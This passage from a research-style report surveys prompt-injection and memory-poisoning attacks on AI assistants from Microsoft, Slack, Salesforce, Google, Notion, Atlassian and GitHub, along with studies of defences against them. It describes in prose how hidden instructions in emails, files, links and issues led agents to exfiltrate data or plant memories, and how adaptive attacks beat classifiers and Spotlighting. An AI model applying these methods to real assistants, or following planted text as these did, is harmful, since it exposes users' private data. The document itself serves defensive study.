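Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes another attack that starts with a link. The link's usual parameter only filled in Copilot's prompt box, so the user still had to press Enter. A second, undocumented parameter made the prompt run immediately. The researchers learned about it by asking Copilot why a prompt could not run by itself, then questioning each explanation until Copilot named the parameter and listed the protections that supposedly disabled it.

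The prompt could make Copilot search services the victim had connected to it, such as Gmail and Google Drive, and send the results out by opening a web address. In one test, Copilot retrieved a password from the body of an email. As with Reprompt, the prompt ran to completion even if the victim closed the tab.

CoSnitch also included a way to plant text in Copilot's memory. In Varonis's demonstration, which didn't use the special link, the victim asked Copilot to summarise a web page containing hidden instructions. Copilot saved the attacker's text to memory and returned a normal-looking summary. Varonis says a prompt in a link could also write to memory, but its research on links focused on stealing data.

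Accounts differ on whether the flaw affected only Copilot Personal or also 365 Copilot, but the evidence for Copilot Personal alone is much stronger. Varonis, which found the flaw, names only that edition. Sri Lanka CERT's *Microsoft Copilot Personal One-Click Data Exfiltration Vulnerability (CoSnitch)*, a government alert, lists the consumer service and personal Microsoft accounts. Waxell's *CoSnitch Copilot Flaw* (2026) reports that Microsoft told the news site Dark Reading that enterprise customers were unaffected. The OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data via AI Prompt Injection* (2026) names both editions, in a summary labelled "AI generated".

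Varonis may have caused some of the confusion by writing that the attack stole data "from enterprises". The attack could still have exposed company data if an employee had connected an account containing work files to Copilot Personal. Microsoft patched the flaw, CVE-2026-24301, on 18 August 2026, eight months after Varonis reported it.

### Why a planted memory outlives the conversation

A language model retains nothing from one conversation to the next, so products provide memory by saving text outside the conversation, such as a note that the user prefers short answers, and adding some of it to the model's context later. If an attacker gets an instruction into this saved text, the product will supply it to the model in later conversations as though it were one of the user's preferences.

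Deleting the original chat does not delete a note that Copilot has saved separately. Changing the password does not delete it either, because the note belongs to the account, and the attacker does not need to log in. Varonis says Copilot Personal's memories never expire. Varonis also showed that a planted memory could make Copilot describe a known security flaw as harmless, which could mislead a user without sending any data out.

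The business version had a similar weakness. Embrace The Red describes how Rehberger planted memories in Microsoft 365 Copilot with a document that looked like a biography of Albert Einstein. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot gave one and asked whether it had been helpful. Copilot saved the attacker's instruction whether the user answered "yes" or "no". Rehberger calls this delayed tool invocation, and uses it because a planted command sometimes gets past safeguards more easily when it runs only after the user's next message.

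The saved instruction told Copilot to send out any password or code the user shared, using the font request that Rehberger had already found in the HTML preview. The attacker could therefore steal secrets that did not yet exist when the victim opened the document. Microsoft reported the memory flaw fixed on 6 December 2025. Once Microsoft had also blocked the font request, a malicious instruction saved earlier could no longer leak data that way, but other planted instructions could still distort Copilot's answers.

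The visible sign of the change was a small "Memory updated" note under the user's message. Memory was on by default, and Microsoft's documentation said in April 2026 that memory actions did not create entries in Purview, its compliance and auditing system. A company that suspected an attack could not simply search those logs for affected employees.

To remove a planted instruction, the user has to delete the saved memory. Microsoft 365 Copilot lists saved memories under the personalisation settings for Copilot chat, where users can delete them individually or turn the feature off. UNU advises reviewing saved memories manually after CoSnitch, and notes that most users never do. It would also be wise to delete the email or document that planted the memory, since Copilot could read it again.

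| Attack | What started it | How long it could continue | What it could reach | What ended it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reprompt | One click on a link | While the server supplied new instructions and the session remained valid | What Copilot Personal knew or could look up about the user | The end of the chain or session, but not closing the tab |
| ChatMate | Uploading a document | Many prompts and answers | The victim's mail, files, calendar and chats | The attacker or Copilot's turn limit |
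| Copilot Cowork | Using a malicious Skill | While its program ran in the background | Outlook, SharePoint, Teams and connected plugins | Ending the background program, but not the stop button |
| CoSnitch link | One click on a link | Until the prompt finished | Connected services, past chats and saved memories | Completion of the prompt |
| Planted memory | Asking about a malicious page or document | Indefinitely | Later conversations, with theft possible if an exit exists | Deleting the memory |

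The table describes the attacks before Microsoft's fixes. An instruction planted in memory lasts longest but gives the attacker the least direct control, because the attacker cannot send new commands through it unless it also makes the assistant contact a server. ReLeak's code chain did connect to a server, but the published accounts describe the connection only as a way to send data out.

### How often planted memories work

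These demonstrations show that memory attacks are possible, but give no success rates. *Trojan Hippo Bench* (Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026) measured success rates with a simulated email assistant that could read, search, send and forward messages.

In each test, the assistant first read one malicious email and stored its instructions. The simulated user then had up to 100 harmless sessions with the assistant before mentioning a sensitive matter, such as income, illness or a court case. The attack counted as a success only if the assistant emailed the attacker all the personal information in that message, with at most small changes in wording.

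The researchers used a language model to write the malicious emails. It proposed eight variants at a time, a program tried them on a practice version of the assistant, and another model scored the results. The process could run for 40 rounds. The researchers then tested the best email on new messages with different personal details.

They compared four kinds of memory:

- An explicit list holds notes that the assistant saves when the user asks it to remember something.
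- Mem0, a widely used open-source system, has a language model extract short facts from each exchange.
- Conversation search, a form of RAG, divides past conversations into passages and retrieves the eight closest to the new message.
- A sliding window keeps the full history in the context and drops the oldest text when space runs out.

The table gives success rates after 100 harmless sessions, with no defence in place. The researchers optimised the emails separately for the first two models, but attacked the larger GPT-5 with the emails optimised for GPT-5-mini.

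| Memory type | Gemini 3.1 Pro | GPT-5-mini | GPT-5, reused emails |
|---|---|---|---|
| Explicit list | 85% | 15% | 5% |
| Mem0 | 80% | 85% | 0% |
| Conversation search | 85% | 80% | 70% |
| Sliding window | 100% | 60% | 35% |
| No memory | 5% | 0% | 0% |

The explicit list most resembles Copilot's saved memories, because the user can read it. The assistant was told to update this list when the user said something like "remember", yet the attack still worked 85 per cent of the time on Gemini. Rehberger recommends that assistants suggest a memory rather than save it, unless the user clearly asked them to. These results suggest that software should enforce such a rule by requiring confirmation, since a malicious email can make the model act as if the user had asked.

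The attack did not fade steadily over time, but the results varied a lot with the order of the harmless sessions. When Das and colleagues shuffled that order in 20 further trials, the standard deviation for conversation search was 43 percentage points. Each main figure averages 60 runs, but these cover only 20 distinct cases, repeated three times, so differences of 5 or 10 points mean little.

The rates also apply to an attacker who knows the assistant's system instructions, tools and type of memory, and can practise on a copy. An outsider attacking Copilot would know less. But the reused emails still worked 70 per cent of the time against GPT-5 with conversation search, even though nobody had adjusted them for that model.

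### What the defences cost

Das and colleagues tested four defences and measured how well the assistant could still do seven kinds of ordinary task. Some tasks needed only memory, while others involved reading mail, sending it or both. The results below are for Gemini 3.1 Pro with conversation search.

| Defence | Attack success | Average task success | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 85% | 99% | None |
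| Store only the user's own messages | 5% | 89% | The assistant often forgets its own earlier suggestions |
| Save nothing from a session that reads mail | 5% | 71% | The assistant cannot later recall facts from that session |
| Limit each memory to 80 characters | 30% | 89% | Longer memories lose meaning |
| Block sending after contact with untrusted text | 0% | 71% | The assistant cannot read mail and then reply without manual help |

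The averages hide some complete failures, so the researchers also calculated the harmonic mean, which gives great weight to low scores and is zero if any one kind of task always fails. It was 88 per cent for the length limit but zero for both defences that averaged 71 per cent.

The length limit was the weakest defence because an attacker could write a shorter instruction. With the explicit list, the limit did not reduce attacks on Gemini. Storing only the user's messages looks like a better choice for an assistant that handles a lot of email, as long as people do not expect it to remember its own proposals. A multi-week plan it wrote, for example, would not be saved.

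The first two defences in the table should have kept the attacker's text out of memory, yet 5 per cent of attacks still succeeded. Attacks on Gemini succeeded at the same rate when it had no memory. The malicious email was probably still in the inbox, where the assistant could read it again during the later session. If so, cleaning the memory would not be enough to stop the attack while the email remained.

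The last defence, a form of information-flow control, also covers that case. Software labels any session that has read mail or retrieved a memory derived from it, then blocks the tools that send messages. The attack failed in every configuration tested because the decision to block those tools did not depend on the model. This works only if the software labels every piece of untrusted text correctly, and it also prevents the assistant from sending a reply to an email it has read.

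## The same weakness in Google, Slack, Salesforce and other products

EchoLeak, SearchLeak, ReLeak and ChatMate all worked against Microsoft's Copilot, but between 2024 and 2026 researchers found the same weakness in assistants from Slack, Google, Salesforce, Notion, Atlassian and GitHub. In each case, an attacker could plant instructions that the assistant followed, and an ordinary feature of the product carried private data out. This suggests that the weakness comes from the way language models read text, whatever model and code a vendor uses, rather than from Microsoft building its assistants less carefully than its competitors.

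Most of these researchers work for firms that sell protection against such attacks, and they publish the attempts that succeed. Their cases can show that many products share the weakness, but not how often an attack would work or which vendor's assistant is safest.

### Who can plant the text

Slack is a workplace chat program that divides a company's conversations into channels, and Slack AI uses those messages to answer questions. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes an attack from August 2024 by someone with an account in the company's Slack workspace. An employee had saved an API key, a kind of password for programs, in a private channel that nobody else could read. The attacker created a public channel, invited no one and posted an instruction there.

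When the employee asked Slack AI for the key, the search returned both messages, because Slack AI also searches public channels that the user has never joined. Slack AI then displayed an error message with a link to log in again. The link's address contained the key, so the attacker received the key if the employee clicked the link.

The answer cited only the employee's own channel as its source. In a second demonstration, Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel, and PromptArmor concluded that its citations were partly random. The EchoLeak attacker had to ask Copilot to hide the source, but here Slack AI apparently omitted it by chance.

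Slack AI began to include uploaded files in its answers on 14 August 2024, the day PromptArmor reported the flaw. PromptArmor thought an outsider with no Slack account could now hide instructions in a PDF and wait for an employee to upload it. The firm had finished its tests before the change, so it had not tested this attack.

Salesforce, which owns Slack, sells software for keeping customer records. Its AI agents, called Agentforce, had a flaw that any member of the public could exploit. Companies can put a Salesforce form on their websites for potential customers, and the answers go straight into the company's records. In ForcedLeak, an attack that the security firm Noma published in September 2025, the attacker typed instructions into this form. When an employee later asked Agentforce about the enquiry, the agent followed the attacker's instructions as well as carrying out the employee's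 request. Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, quotes Noma's view that "predictable employee queries" helped the attack, since someone will sooner or later ask about a new enquiry.

The agent collected details of other potential customers and put them in the address of an image. Agentforce's content security policy should have blocked the request, but it still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. According to Nudge Security's *ForcedLeak indirect prompt injection in Salesforce Agentforce* (2025), an attacker could acquire that domain. The attacker could then receive the data directly, whereas in EchoLeak, Aim Labs had to find a Microsoft service to relay it. Because domains can change hands, a list of allowed domains needs checking even when nobody has edited it.

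Noma reported ForcedLeak on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce fixed it on 8 September. Salesforce regained control of the expired domain and stopped its agents from sending output to untrusted addresses (The Hacker News, 2025). These measures blocked the route by which data left, but the public could still write text that the agent would read. OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026), a machine-written summary, reports that Capsule Security later found another way to steal data from Agentforce through a public form. Capsule found a similar flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Studio, and both companies issued patches.

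Google's assistants also read text that strangers can send. Noma found the GeminiJack flaw in June 2025 and reported it to Google the same day, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data*. It affected Gemini Enterprise (Google's AI assistant tools for companies) and Vertex AI Search (a platform for building search tools). An attacker could put instructions in an email, a shared document or a calendar invitation, and they took effect when an employee ran a routine search, according to SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*. Gemini could then leak the emails, calendar entries and documents it found by including them in the address of an image.

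SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Gemini Enterprise Vulnerability Exposing Corporate Data* reports that Noma called GeminiJack "an architectural weakness". Google separated Vertex AI Search from Gemini Enterprise so that the two products no longer shared a retrieval system, a broader fix than blocking one image.

Ben Nassi, Stav Cohen and Or Yair had already attacked Google's Gemini through calendar invitations. In *Invitation Is All You Need* (2025), they hid instructions in the invitations' titles and waited for the user to ask Gemini about upcoming meetings. In their demonstrations, Gemini deleted appointments, operated the lights and boiler in a smart home, and sent out information from the user's email. Google added defences before they published the paper.

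A later attack by the firm Miggo Security used calendar invitations both to deliver instructions and to extract data. According to Hackread's *Google Gemini AI Tricked Into Leaking Calendar Data via Meeting Invites*, Gemini followed hidden instructions in an invitation, created a new meeting and pasted the user's private calendar data into it, while telling the user only that a time slot was free. The attacker could read the data if the company's settings made the new meeting visible to them. A list of approved sites would not have helped, because no browser had to contact an unfamiliar server. Google has since fixed the flaw.

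### Safeguards that missed the request

Notion, a program for shared notes and databases, has had to fix two leaks of this kind. In September 2025 it released version 3.0, with AI agents that could carry out tasks on their own. A day later, Willison covered the first attack on them in *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*. Abi Raghuram of the firm CodeIntegrity had made a PDF that looked like a customer feedback report and contained instructions in white text. When a user uploaded it and asked for a summary, the agent read a list of the company's clients, put their names and revenue into a web address, and opened that address with its web search tool. The agent ran on Claude Sonnet 4, then a leading model from Anthropic.

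Notion responded within days. According to The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025), it improved its detection of hidden instructions and required the user's approval before an agent opened a suspicious link or one the model had written. Administrators could also turn off web access for agents.

The second attack, in January 2026, did not need the agent to open a link. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a CV with instructions in one-point white type, covered by a white image. A recruiter uploaded the CV and asked Notion AI to update a hiring tracker, a page of notes on all the candidates. Notion AI put the tracker's text in an image address and inserted the image into the page.

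Notion asked the recruiter whether to trust the outside site. But by then it had saved the edit and the recruiter's browser had requested the image, so refusing made no difference. The attacker's log contained salary expectations, comments on candidates and the company's diversity hiring goals. SearchLeak depended on a similar mistake in the order of events.

Notion AI used a language model to scan uploaded files for malicious instructions. PromptArmor did not try to defeat this scan, because an attacker could avoid it by putting the instructions on a web page or in another source that Notion did not seem to scan. PromptArmor also found that the drafting assistant in Notion Mail displayed outside images, although it appeared to read only pages the user named. Notion fixed the flaw in document edits on the night of 7 January. PromptArmor lists no fix for Notion Mail in its timeline.

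Turning off a feature in Rovo, Atlassian's assistant, can leave part of it running. Atlassian makes Jira, which tracks tasks, and Confluence, which stores shared documents. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, published in August 2026, describes an attack in which a user uploads a guide found online and asks Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Hidden text in the guide makes Rovo add the contents of tickets and documents to the attacker's web address and then open that address. The user sees sensible suggestions for the tickets and no trace of the theft.

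The attack worked even when an administrator had turned off web search for the whole organisation. PromptArmor explains that the setting removed Rovo's ability to search but left the tool that opens search results. Nothing checked whether Rovo had made up the address. Rehberger recommends that Copilot be allowed to open only addresses already in a public search index, and the same rule in Rovo would have blocked the made-up address.

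The Hacker News (2026) notes that only PromptArmor has reported this bypass, and that Atlassian does not say in its documentation whether the setting covers addresses that Rovo composes. It also objects to PromptArmor calling the attack "zero-click", since the victim has to upload the malicious file. That objection is reasonable. People do upload files they have found online, but an attacker who publishes a guide has to wait for someone to find and upload it, while one who sends an EchoLeak email can choose the victim.

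Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes another attack on Rovo, using a link containing a prompt that Rovo ran as soon as a logged-in user clicked it, just as Copilot had done in Reprompt. The attacker did not need to know the victim's organisation, because Atlassian filled in the victim's default one if the link left it blank. In the demonstration, Rovo found a private API key in Confluence and sent it out in an image address.

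The same technique worked on data that Rovo could reach through its connections to SharePoint and Outlook, according to The Hacker News. A company could therefore lose Microsoft 365 data through a flaw in Atlassian's product, even if Microsoft had repaired every flaw in Copilot. Varonis counts more than 50 platforms that customers can connect to Rovo. It also found that Rovo usually followed the prompt even when it was not disguised, whereas Taler needed the bird puzzle and repeated requests to get data out of Copilot Personal.

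A trusted website can also receive stolen data without forwarding it anywhere. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which Superhuman's email assistant submitted the user's messages to a Google Form that the attacker had created. The attacker then read them as form responses, without needing a server. A filter that trusted all Google addresses would have allowed this. Superhuman fixed the flaw quickly.

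### An agent with more access than its victim

In the Slack and Rovo attacks, the assistant used the permissions of the person who asked the question, as Copilot does. An agent that runs automatically may have its own permissions, which can be much broader.

GitHub, which Microsoft owns, stores software code in collections called repositories. A company may make some of them public and keep others private. Anyone can usually post an "issue" on a public repository to report a fault or ask for a change. In 2026, GitHub introduced Agentic Workflows, in which an AI agent reads these issues and acts on them, following instructions that the repository's owner has written in plain English.

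Levi's *GitLost* describes how Noma used an issue to get private files out of this system. Working with their own repositories, the researchers set up a workflow that started whenever a person or an automated rule assigned an issue. According to InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026), the agent could read the issue, reply with a comment, and read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

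The issue looked like a message from a vice-president of sales after a meeting with a customer. Among other requests, it asked for the contents of the README, or introductory file, in a private repository. The agent fetched the file and posted its contents as a public comment. The attacker didn't need an account at the company and only had to read the comment.

This way of getting data out is even simpler than using an image or a Google Form, because publishing comments was the agent's job. The address filters and content security policies that might have stopped the other attacks do not apply here. To stop this attack, GitHub would have had to check whether the comment's text came from a private source.

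GitHub Copilot, which ran the agent, refused the request when it appeared alone. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that the same request succeeded when it began with the word "Additionally". Noma thinks the word made the request look like a continuation of the agent's task. This is plausible, since Ye and colleagues found that a passage's style can affect whether a model obeys it. But the published accounts do not give the number of times Noma tried each version. Models often answer the same prompt differently each time, so the word may have mattered less than the headlines suggest.

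A similar attack had worked a year earlier on agents that individual developers ran. Willison's *GitHub MCP Exploited* describes how Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner planted an issue asking for more publicity for a project's author. An agent that read the issue could reveal information from the author's private repositories. That agent had one developer's access. In GitLost, what an attacker could steal depended on what the company had allowed the workflow to read, so developers could not limit the damage by restricting their own permissions.

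GitHub had planned for prompt injection. As Expert Insights notes, GitHub's guidance tells companies to give agents as little access as possible, and GitHub separates the agent from the step that publishes anything. The separation did not help here because the workflow had permission to publish comments, and nothing would have made the publishing step reject one.

*Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, describes a stricter design, in which software labels every item by how secret it is and how far to trust its author. An agent that has read secret material may write only to places labelled at least as secret. Under that rule, the agent in GitLost could have read the private README but could not then have posted a public comment.

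### Flaw or intended behaviour

Vendors have disagreed with researchers about whether some of these leaks were flaws. Slack asked PromptArmor two rounds of questions and concluded on 19 August 2024 that the evidence was insufficient. It said that any member of a workspace may search its public channels and called this "intended behavior". Slack was right about the search, but PromptArmor had reported the theft of a key from a private channel. Slack seems to have misunderstood the demonstration, because it said that the information in the first video was already public.

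PromptArmor published its report the next day, and Slack issued a patch within hours. In a statement on 21 August, Slack (2024) said that the attack required an existing account and "very limited and specific circumstances". The company said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. Requiring an account limited the risk, but less so in a workspace with thousands of employees and contractors.

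A failure of communication delayed Notion's fix. HackerOne, which receives security reports for other companies, closed PromptArmor's report as "Not Applicable" on 29 December 2025. PromptArmor later learned that the report had apparently never reached Notion. When PromptArmor published it on 7 January, Notion confirmed the flaw and deployed a fix that night. This suggests the delay had little to do with how hard the flaw was to fix.

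Atlassian fixed the Rovo link flaw on its servers on 8 July 2026, and the report earned a $6,000 reward. PromptArmor had reported the file attack on 23 May and received a case number, but it says Atlassian did not answer two later messages. The Hacker News found no confirmation of a fix as of 8 August. The link flaw was easier to fix because Atlassian could stop Rovo from running text in one parameter. Rovo has to read uploaded files, so to stop the file attack, Atlassian would need to restrict the addresses Rovo can open.

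The dispute over GitLost is harder to settle. Noma calls it a critical vulnerability, while Expert Insights describes the workflow as misconfigured. Noma proposed a note in GitHub's documentation, rather than a code change, to warn companies about sharing access between repositories. On 8 July 2026, The Next Web's *'GitLost'* reported that GitHub had not added one. Kiteworks' *GitHub's AI Agent Leaked Private Code With One Word* says that GitHub later updated its documentation, but that Noma considers the design flaw still present.

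Both descriptions are partly true. The company that set up the workflow chose to give it access to private code, and removing that access would stop the attack. But the product is designed to let agents read and reply to strangers' posts, and many customers will not realise that a reply could reveal any private file the agent can read. The labels that GitHub Next describes would protect those customers even if they did not foresee the attack.

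Attackers get into all these products in much the same way, whether the model comes from Google, Anthropic or another company. The ShadowLeak attack exploited the same weakness in OpenAI's ChatGPT. This is good evidence that the attacks rely on a general class of flaw rather than a mistake in one vendor's code.

The ways data gets out depend much more on the vendor. Salesforce trusted an expired domain, Notion saved an edit before asking the user to approve it, and Atlassian left a tool running after an administrator had turned off the search it belonged to. These are ordinary programming and management mistakes, so vendors could often fix them in days. But the assistants still read text from outsiders after the fixes, so a different flaw could leak data again, as happened within months with both Agentforce and Notion AI.

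| Case | Who could plant text, and where | Data within reach | Exit | Vendor's response and fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Slack AI, 2024 | A member of the workspace, in a public channel | Private messages the user could read | A link the user clicked | Reviewed the report and called the search "intended behavior"; patched on the day of publication |
| ForcedLeak (Salesforce), 2025 | Anyone, in a web form | Records of potential customers | An image on an expired domain that Salesforce still trusted | Recovered the domain and restricted outgoing addresses |
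| GeminiJack (Google), 2025 | Anyone able to send an email or invitation, or share a document | Emails, calendars and documents | An image address | Accepted as a flaw; separated the two affected products |
| Notion agents, 2025 | The author of a PDF that a user uploaded | Client names and revenue | The web search tool | Better detection, and approval for suspicious links |
| Notion AI, 2026 | The author of a CV that a user uploaded | The hiring tracker | An image saved before the user approved it | HackerOne closed the report; Notion fixed document edits after publication |
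| Rovo file attack (Atlassian), 2026 | The author of a file that a user uploaded | Whatever the user could reach in Jira, Confluence and connected services | The tool for opening web addresses | Gave the report a case number; no confirmed fix as of 8 August 2026 |
| RovoBlast (Atlassian), 2026 | Anyone who could get the user to click a link | The same | An image address | Accepted as a flaw; fixed on 8 July 2026 |
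| GitLost (GitHub), 2026 | Anyone, in a public issue | Every repository the workflow could read | A public comment | Reportedly updated its documentation; Noma says the design flaw remains |

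## Filters and training that try to recognise malicious instructions

Blocking a route by which data can leave doesn't change what the assistant reads, so Microsoft, Google and OpenAI also try to stop planted instructions from working. A classifier can screen outside text before the model reads it. Software can also mark the text to show its source, a technique Microsoft calls Spotlighting. Developers can train a model to ignore instructions in the material it reads.

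In its July 2025 account, Microsoft describes layered defences. It uses Spotlighting and carefully written system instructions to prevent prompt injection, and a classifier called Prompt Shields to detect it. If both fail, restricted permissions, blocked routes for sending data out and user approval are supposed to limit the damage. Prevention and detection both depend on telling malicious instructions from the many ordinary ones in business email.

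### Classifiers

Microsoft sells Prompt Shields to developers through Azure, its cloud service. In *Safeguarding AI against ‘jailbreaks’ and other prompt attacks*, Ho describes it as a fine-tuned model, meaning an existing model that Microsoft trained further specifically to recognise malicious instructions. Microsoft trained it on known injection techniques in several languages and keeps adding new ones. Copilot's XPIA classifier, which Aim Labs' email evaded in EchoLeak, serves the same purpose.

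The assistant's software sends each piece of outside text to the classifier before the language model receives it. The classifier typically returns a score for how closely the text resembles an attack, and the software compares that score with a threshold. If the score is below the threshold, the software adds the text to the model's context. If the score is above it, the software has to block the text or take another precaution, and it can also alert the company's security team. Lowering the threshold catches more attacks but also flags more ordinary mail.

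Other detectors use more than the wording. An "LLM judge" is a general language model that a developer asks to decide whether an email contains an injection. TaskTracker compares the assistant's internal activity before and after it reads the outside text, and uses a small classifier to check for signs that the assistant's task has changed.

### Spotlighting

*Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (Hines, Lopez and colleagues, 2024) proposed three ways to mark outside text. In each, the system instructions explain the marking and tell the model not to obey marked text. The table shows what the model would receive if an email contained the words "The revised offer", and how often attacks succeeded when GPT-3.5-Turbo, an older OpenAI model, summarised documents.

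| Method | What the model receives | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| No marking | The revised offer | 50–60% |
| Delimiting: symbols at each end | <<The revised offer>> | About half as high |
| Datamarking: a symbol between words | The^revised^offer | 3.1% |
| Encoding: the text in base64 | VGhlIHJldmlzZWQgb2ZmZXI= | 0.0% |

When the same model answered questions about documents, 8.0 per cent of attacks got past datamarking and 1.8 per cent got past encoding. Datamarking did not measurably worsen the model's performance on ordinary tasks. Encoding badly impaired GPT-3.5-Turbo, which made decoding mistakes, while the stronger GPT-4 mostly handled it.

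These results were encouraging in 2024, but the attacks were simple. Hines and colleagues generated 1,000 documents, each containing a variation of an instruction to forget the task and reply with a single keyword. They counted an attack as successful only if it took over the whole answer, so a proper summary that also mentioned the keyword counted as a failed attack. An attacker like the one in EchoLeak wants that kind of answer, a normal reply with a small addition. Hines and colleagues report that a looser measure showed the same trends.

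They also considered an attacker who knows the system instructions and could defeat delimiting by typing the closing symbol. They therefore advise against delimiting and suggest choosing a new random marker for each request. Five characters drawn from 20 symbols would give 20^5, or 3.2 million, possible markers. But an attacker doesn't have to forge the marker if the model will obey marked text anyway, and Ye and colleagues found that the style of a passage can outweigh its label.

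Hines and colleagues compare the problem with early telephone networks, which carried control signals on the same line as callers' voices. Engineers put the two at different frequencies, which prevented accidental interference, but people who could imitate the control tones made free calls. Telephone companies later moved the control signals to a separate channel. Language models have no separate channel for instructions, and Hines and colleagues see no straightforward way to add one to current designs. They accept that Spotlighting, like the use of different frequencies, is not secure against deliberate interference. Microsoft has since offered Spotlighting to developers in a public preview as part of Prompt Shields.

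### Training a model to ignore planted instructions

Shi, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, explain how Google trained its Gemini 2.5 model to resist such attacks:

1. They created many realistic conversations in which an assistant used tools such as email and calendars, and included invented private information.
2. Automated attack programs wrote thousands of planted instructions that made the model try to leak this information.
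3. For each successful attack, they produced a safe answer by warning the model not to reveal private data. A second model then discarded any answer that still followed the attacker or failed to do what the user had asked.
4. They trained Gemini on the attacks paired with the safe answers, and used reinforcement learning, which rewards good behaviour, as well.

Google first tested the resulting model, Gemini 2.5, with 1,799 prompts containing attacks prepared against the previous model, Gemini 2.0. The attacks' success rate fell from 92 to 18 per cent. The researchers then used the attack programs to develop new attacks against Gemini 2.5 itself. In these tests, the attacker tried to steal a passport number through an email or a calendar entry. Each program could query the model thousands of times while developing an attack, and the researchers tested its best attack on conversations that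 had not been used to develop it.

| Attack program | Email: Gemini 2.0 | Email: Gemini 2.5 | Calendar: Gemini 2.0 | Calendar: Gemini 2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| TAP (natural language) | 99.8% | 53.6% | 100% | 94.6% |
| Actor Critic (natural language) | 66.2% | 40.8% | 96.8% | 59.6% |
| Beam Search (random tokens) | 74.8% | 4.2% | 98.6% | 0% |

Google's training lowered the attacks' success rate by 47 percentage points on average, but an attacker would choose the method that works best. That method still succeeded almost every time against the calendar tool, which Google had left out of the training data. Training worked much better against strings of random tokens than against the plausible sentences that an attacker would use when writing to an office worker.

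A warning after the outside text, telling the model not to expose private information, cut TAP's success in the calendar test to 6.2 per cent. With the same warning, TAP had succeeded 10.8 per cent of the time on Gemini 2.0, so training and the warning worked better together. However, the warning might also make the model refuse when a user wants to send private information to someone they trust.

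Google tested the models without the safeguards that surround them in its products. Shi and colleagues found that the training did not noticeably reduce the models' general ability. They also found that more capable models are not automatically safer, and that models which follow instructions well are sometimes easier to attack.

### A contest with an email assistant

Google's attackers were programs, whereas *LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) describes a contest in which 839 people attacked a simulated email assistant between December 2024 and April 2025. Microsoft researchers were among the organisers. Participants wrote emails intended to make the assistant send a message its user had not requested. In one version of the task, the message had to include a profit forecast from another email in the mailbox.

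Participants knew which defences they faced and could try as often as they liked. After each attempt they learned whether the assistant had retrieved the email, whether a defence had caught it, and how much of the unauthorised message was correct. They could not see the assistant's answer or the exact name of its email tool.

In the first phase, teams made 370,724 submissions, of which about 3,000 (less than 1 per cent) succeeded from start to finish. This rate overstates the defences' strength, because teams spent most of their attempts learning what would work. The share of teams that eventually succeeded is a better guide to what a persistent attacker could do.

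The table shows team success on the profit-forecast task with GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model. The number of attempts is an average across all first-phase tasks among teams that succeeded. For the last two columns, the researchers reran the detectors on first-phase attacks that had triggered the email tool, and then on 1,000 ordinary emails from the Enron collection.

| Defence | Teams that succeeded | Failed attempts before first success | Attacks detected | Ordinary emails flagged |
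|---|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft's text classifier | 60% | 89 | 60–68% | 0% |
| Spotlighting | 53% | – | – | – |
| TaskTracker | 44% | 159 | 76–95% | 4–6% |
| LLM judge | 32% | 506 | 99.4% | 5% |
| All together | 17% | – | 99.8% | 10% |

The detection and false-alarm tests may have used different thresholds, so the last two columns do not show an exact trade-off. The average numbers of attempts also cover a very wide range, from teams that got through quickly to teams that needed thousands of tries.

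The classifier was the weakest detector, but it flagged none of the Enron emails. It struggled because attacks don't always use obviously malicious wording. In one successful attack, a friendly colleague called Nate asks for a confirmation to go out at once because the boss is shouting, and promises pizza and beer in return.

Emails disguised well enough to get past the defences were often too vague to control the model. The assistant tried to send the unauthorised message in about 19 per cent of the submissions that the defences detected, but in only 4 per cent of those they missed.

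For the second phase, the organisers strengthened the defences and blocked close copies of earlier attacks. Nobody got past the full set of defences on GPT-4o-mini. This was the contest's best result for layered filters, but the combined detectors had flagged one in ten of the Enron emails, which Abdelnabi and colleagues consider too many for real use. The attackers had also improved, and the text classifier's two versions caught only 43 and 49 per cent of the successful tool calls in this phase.

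The researchers later replayed attacks from the contest on models that were not in it. The attacks worked 58 per cent of the time on GPT-4o, 47 per cent on GPT-5 mini and 23 per cent on GPT-5. They also worked 32 per cent of the time on Meta SecAlign, which its developers had trained specifically to resist injection. In earlier tests, attacks on that model had worked less than 5 per cent of the time.

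### Attacks adapted to each defence

Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) argue in *The Attacker Moves Second* that a defence should be tested against an attacker who knows how it works and has plenty of time and computing power. The group, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, retested 12 published defences, two designed against jailbreaks and the rest against prompt injection.

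In one method, a language model wrote several candidate instructions, a program tried them against the defended assistant, and the language model rewrote the ones that came closest to working. This cycle repeated. When the defence was a classifier, the attacker also received its confidence score. In a separate competition, more than 500 people tried to break the defences by hand.

| Defence | How it works | Success with fixed attacks | Success with adapted attacks |
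|---|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by source | About 1% | Over 95% |
| Meta SecAlign | Trains the model | 2% | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor | Screen text with a classifier | – | Over 90% |
| PIGuard | Screens text with a classifier | – | 71% |

Many of the winning instructions looked like office procedure. One that got past a classifier cited a company policy that anyone rescheduling a meeting had to delete a tracking file. A classifier that flagged such text would also flag a lot of genuine company policy.

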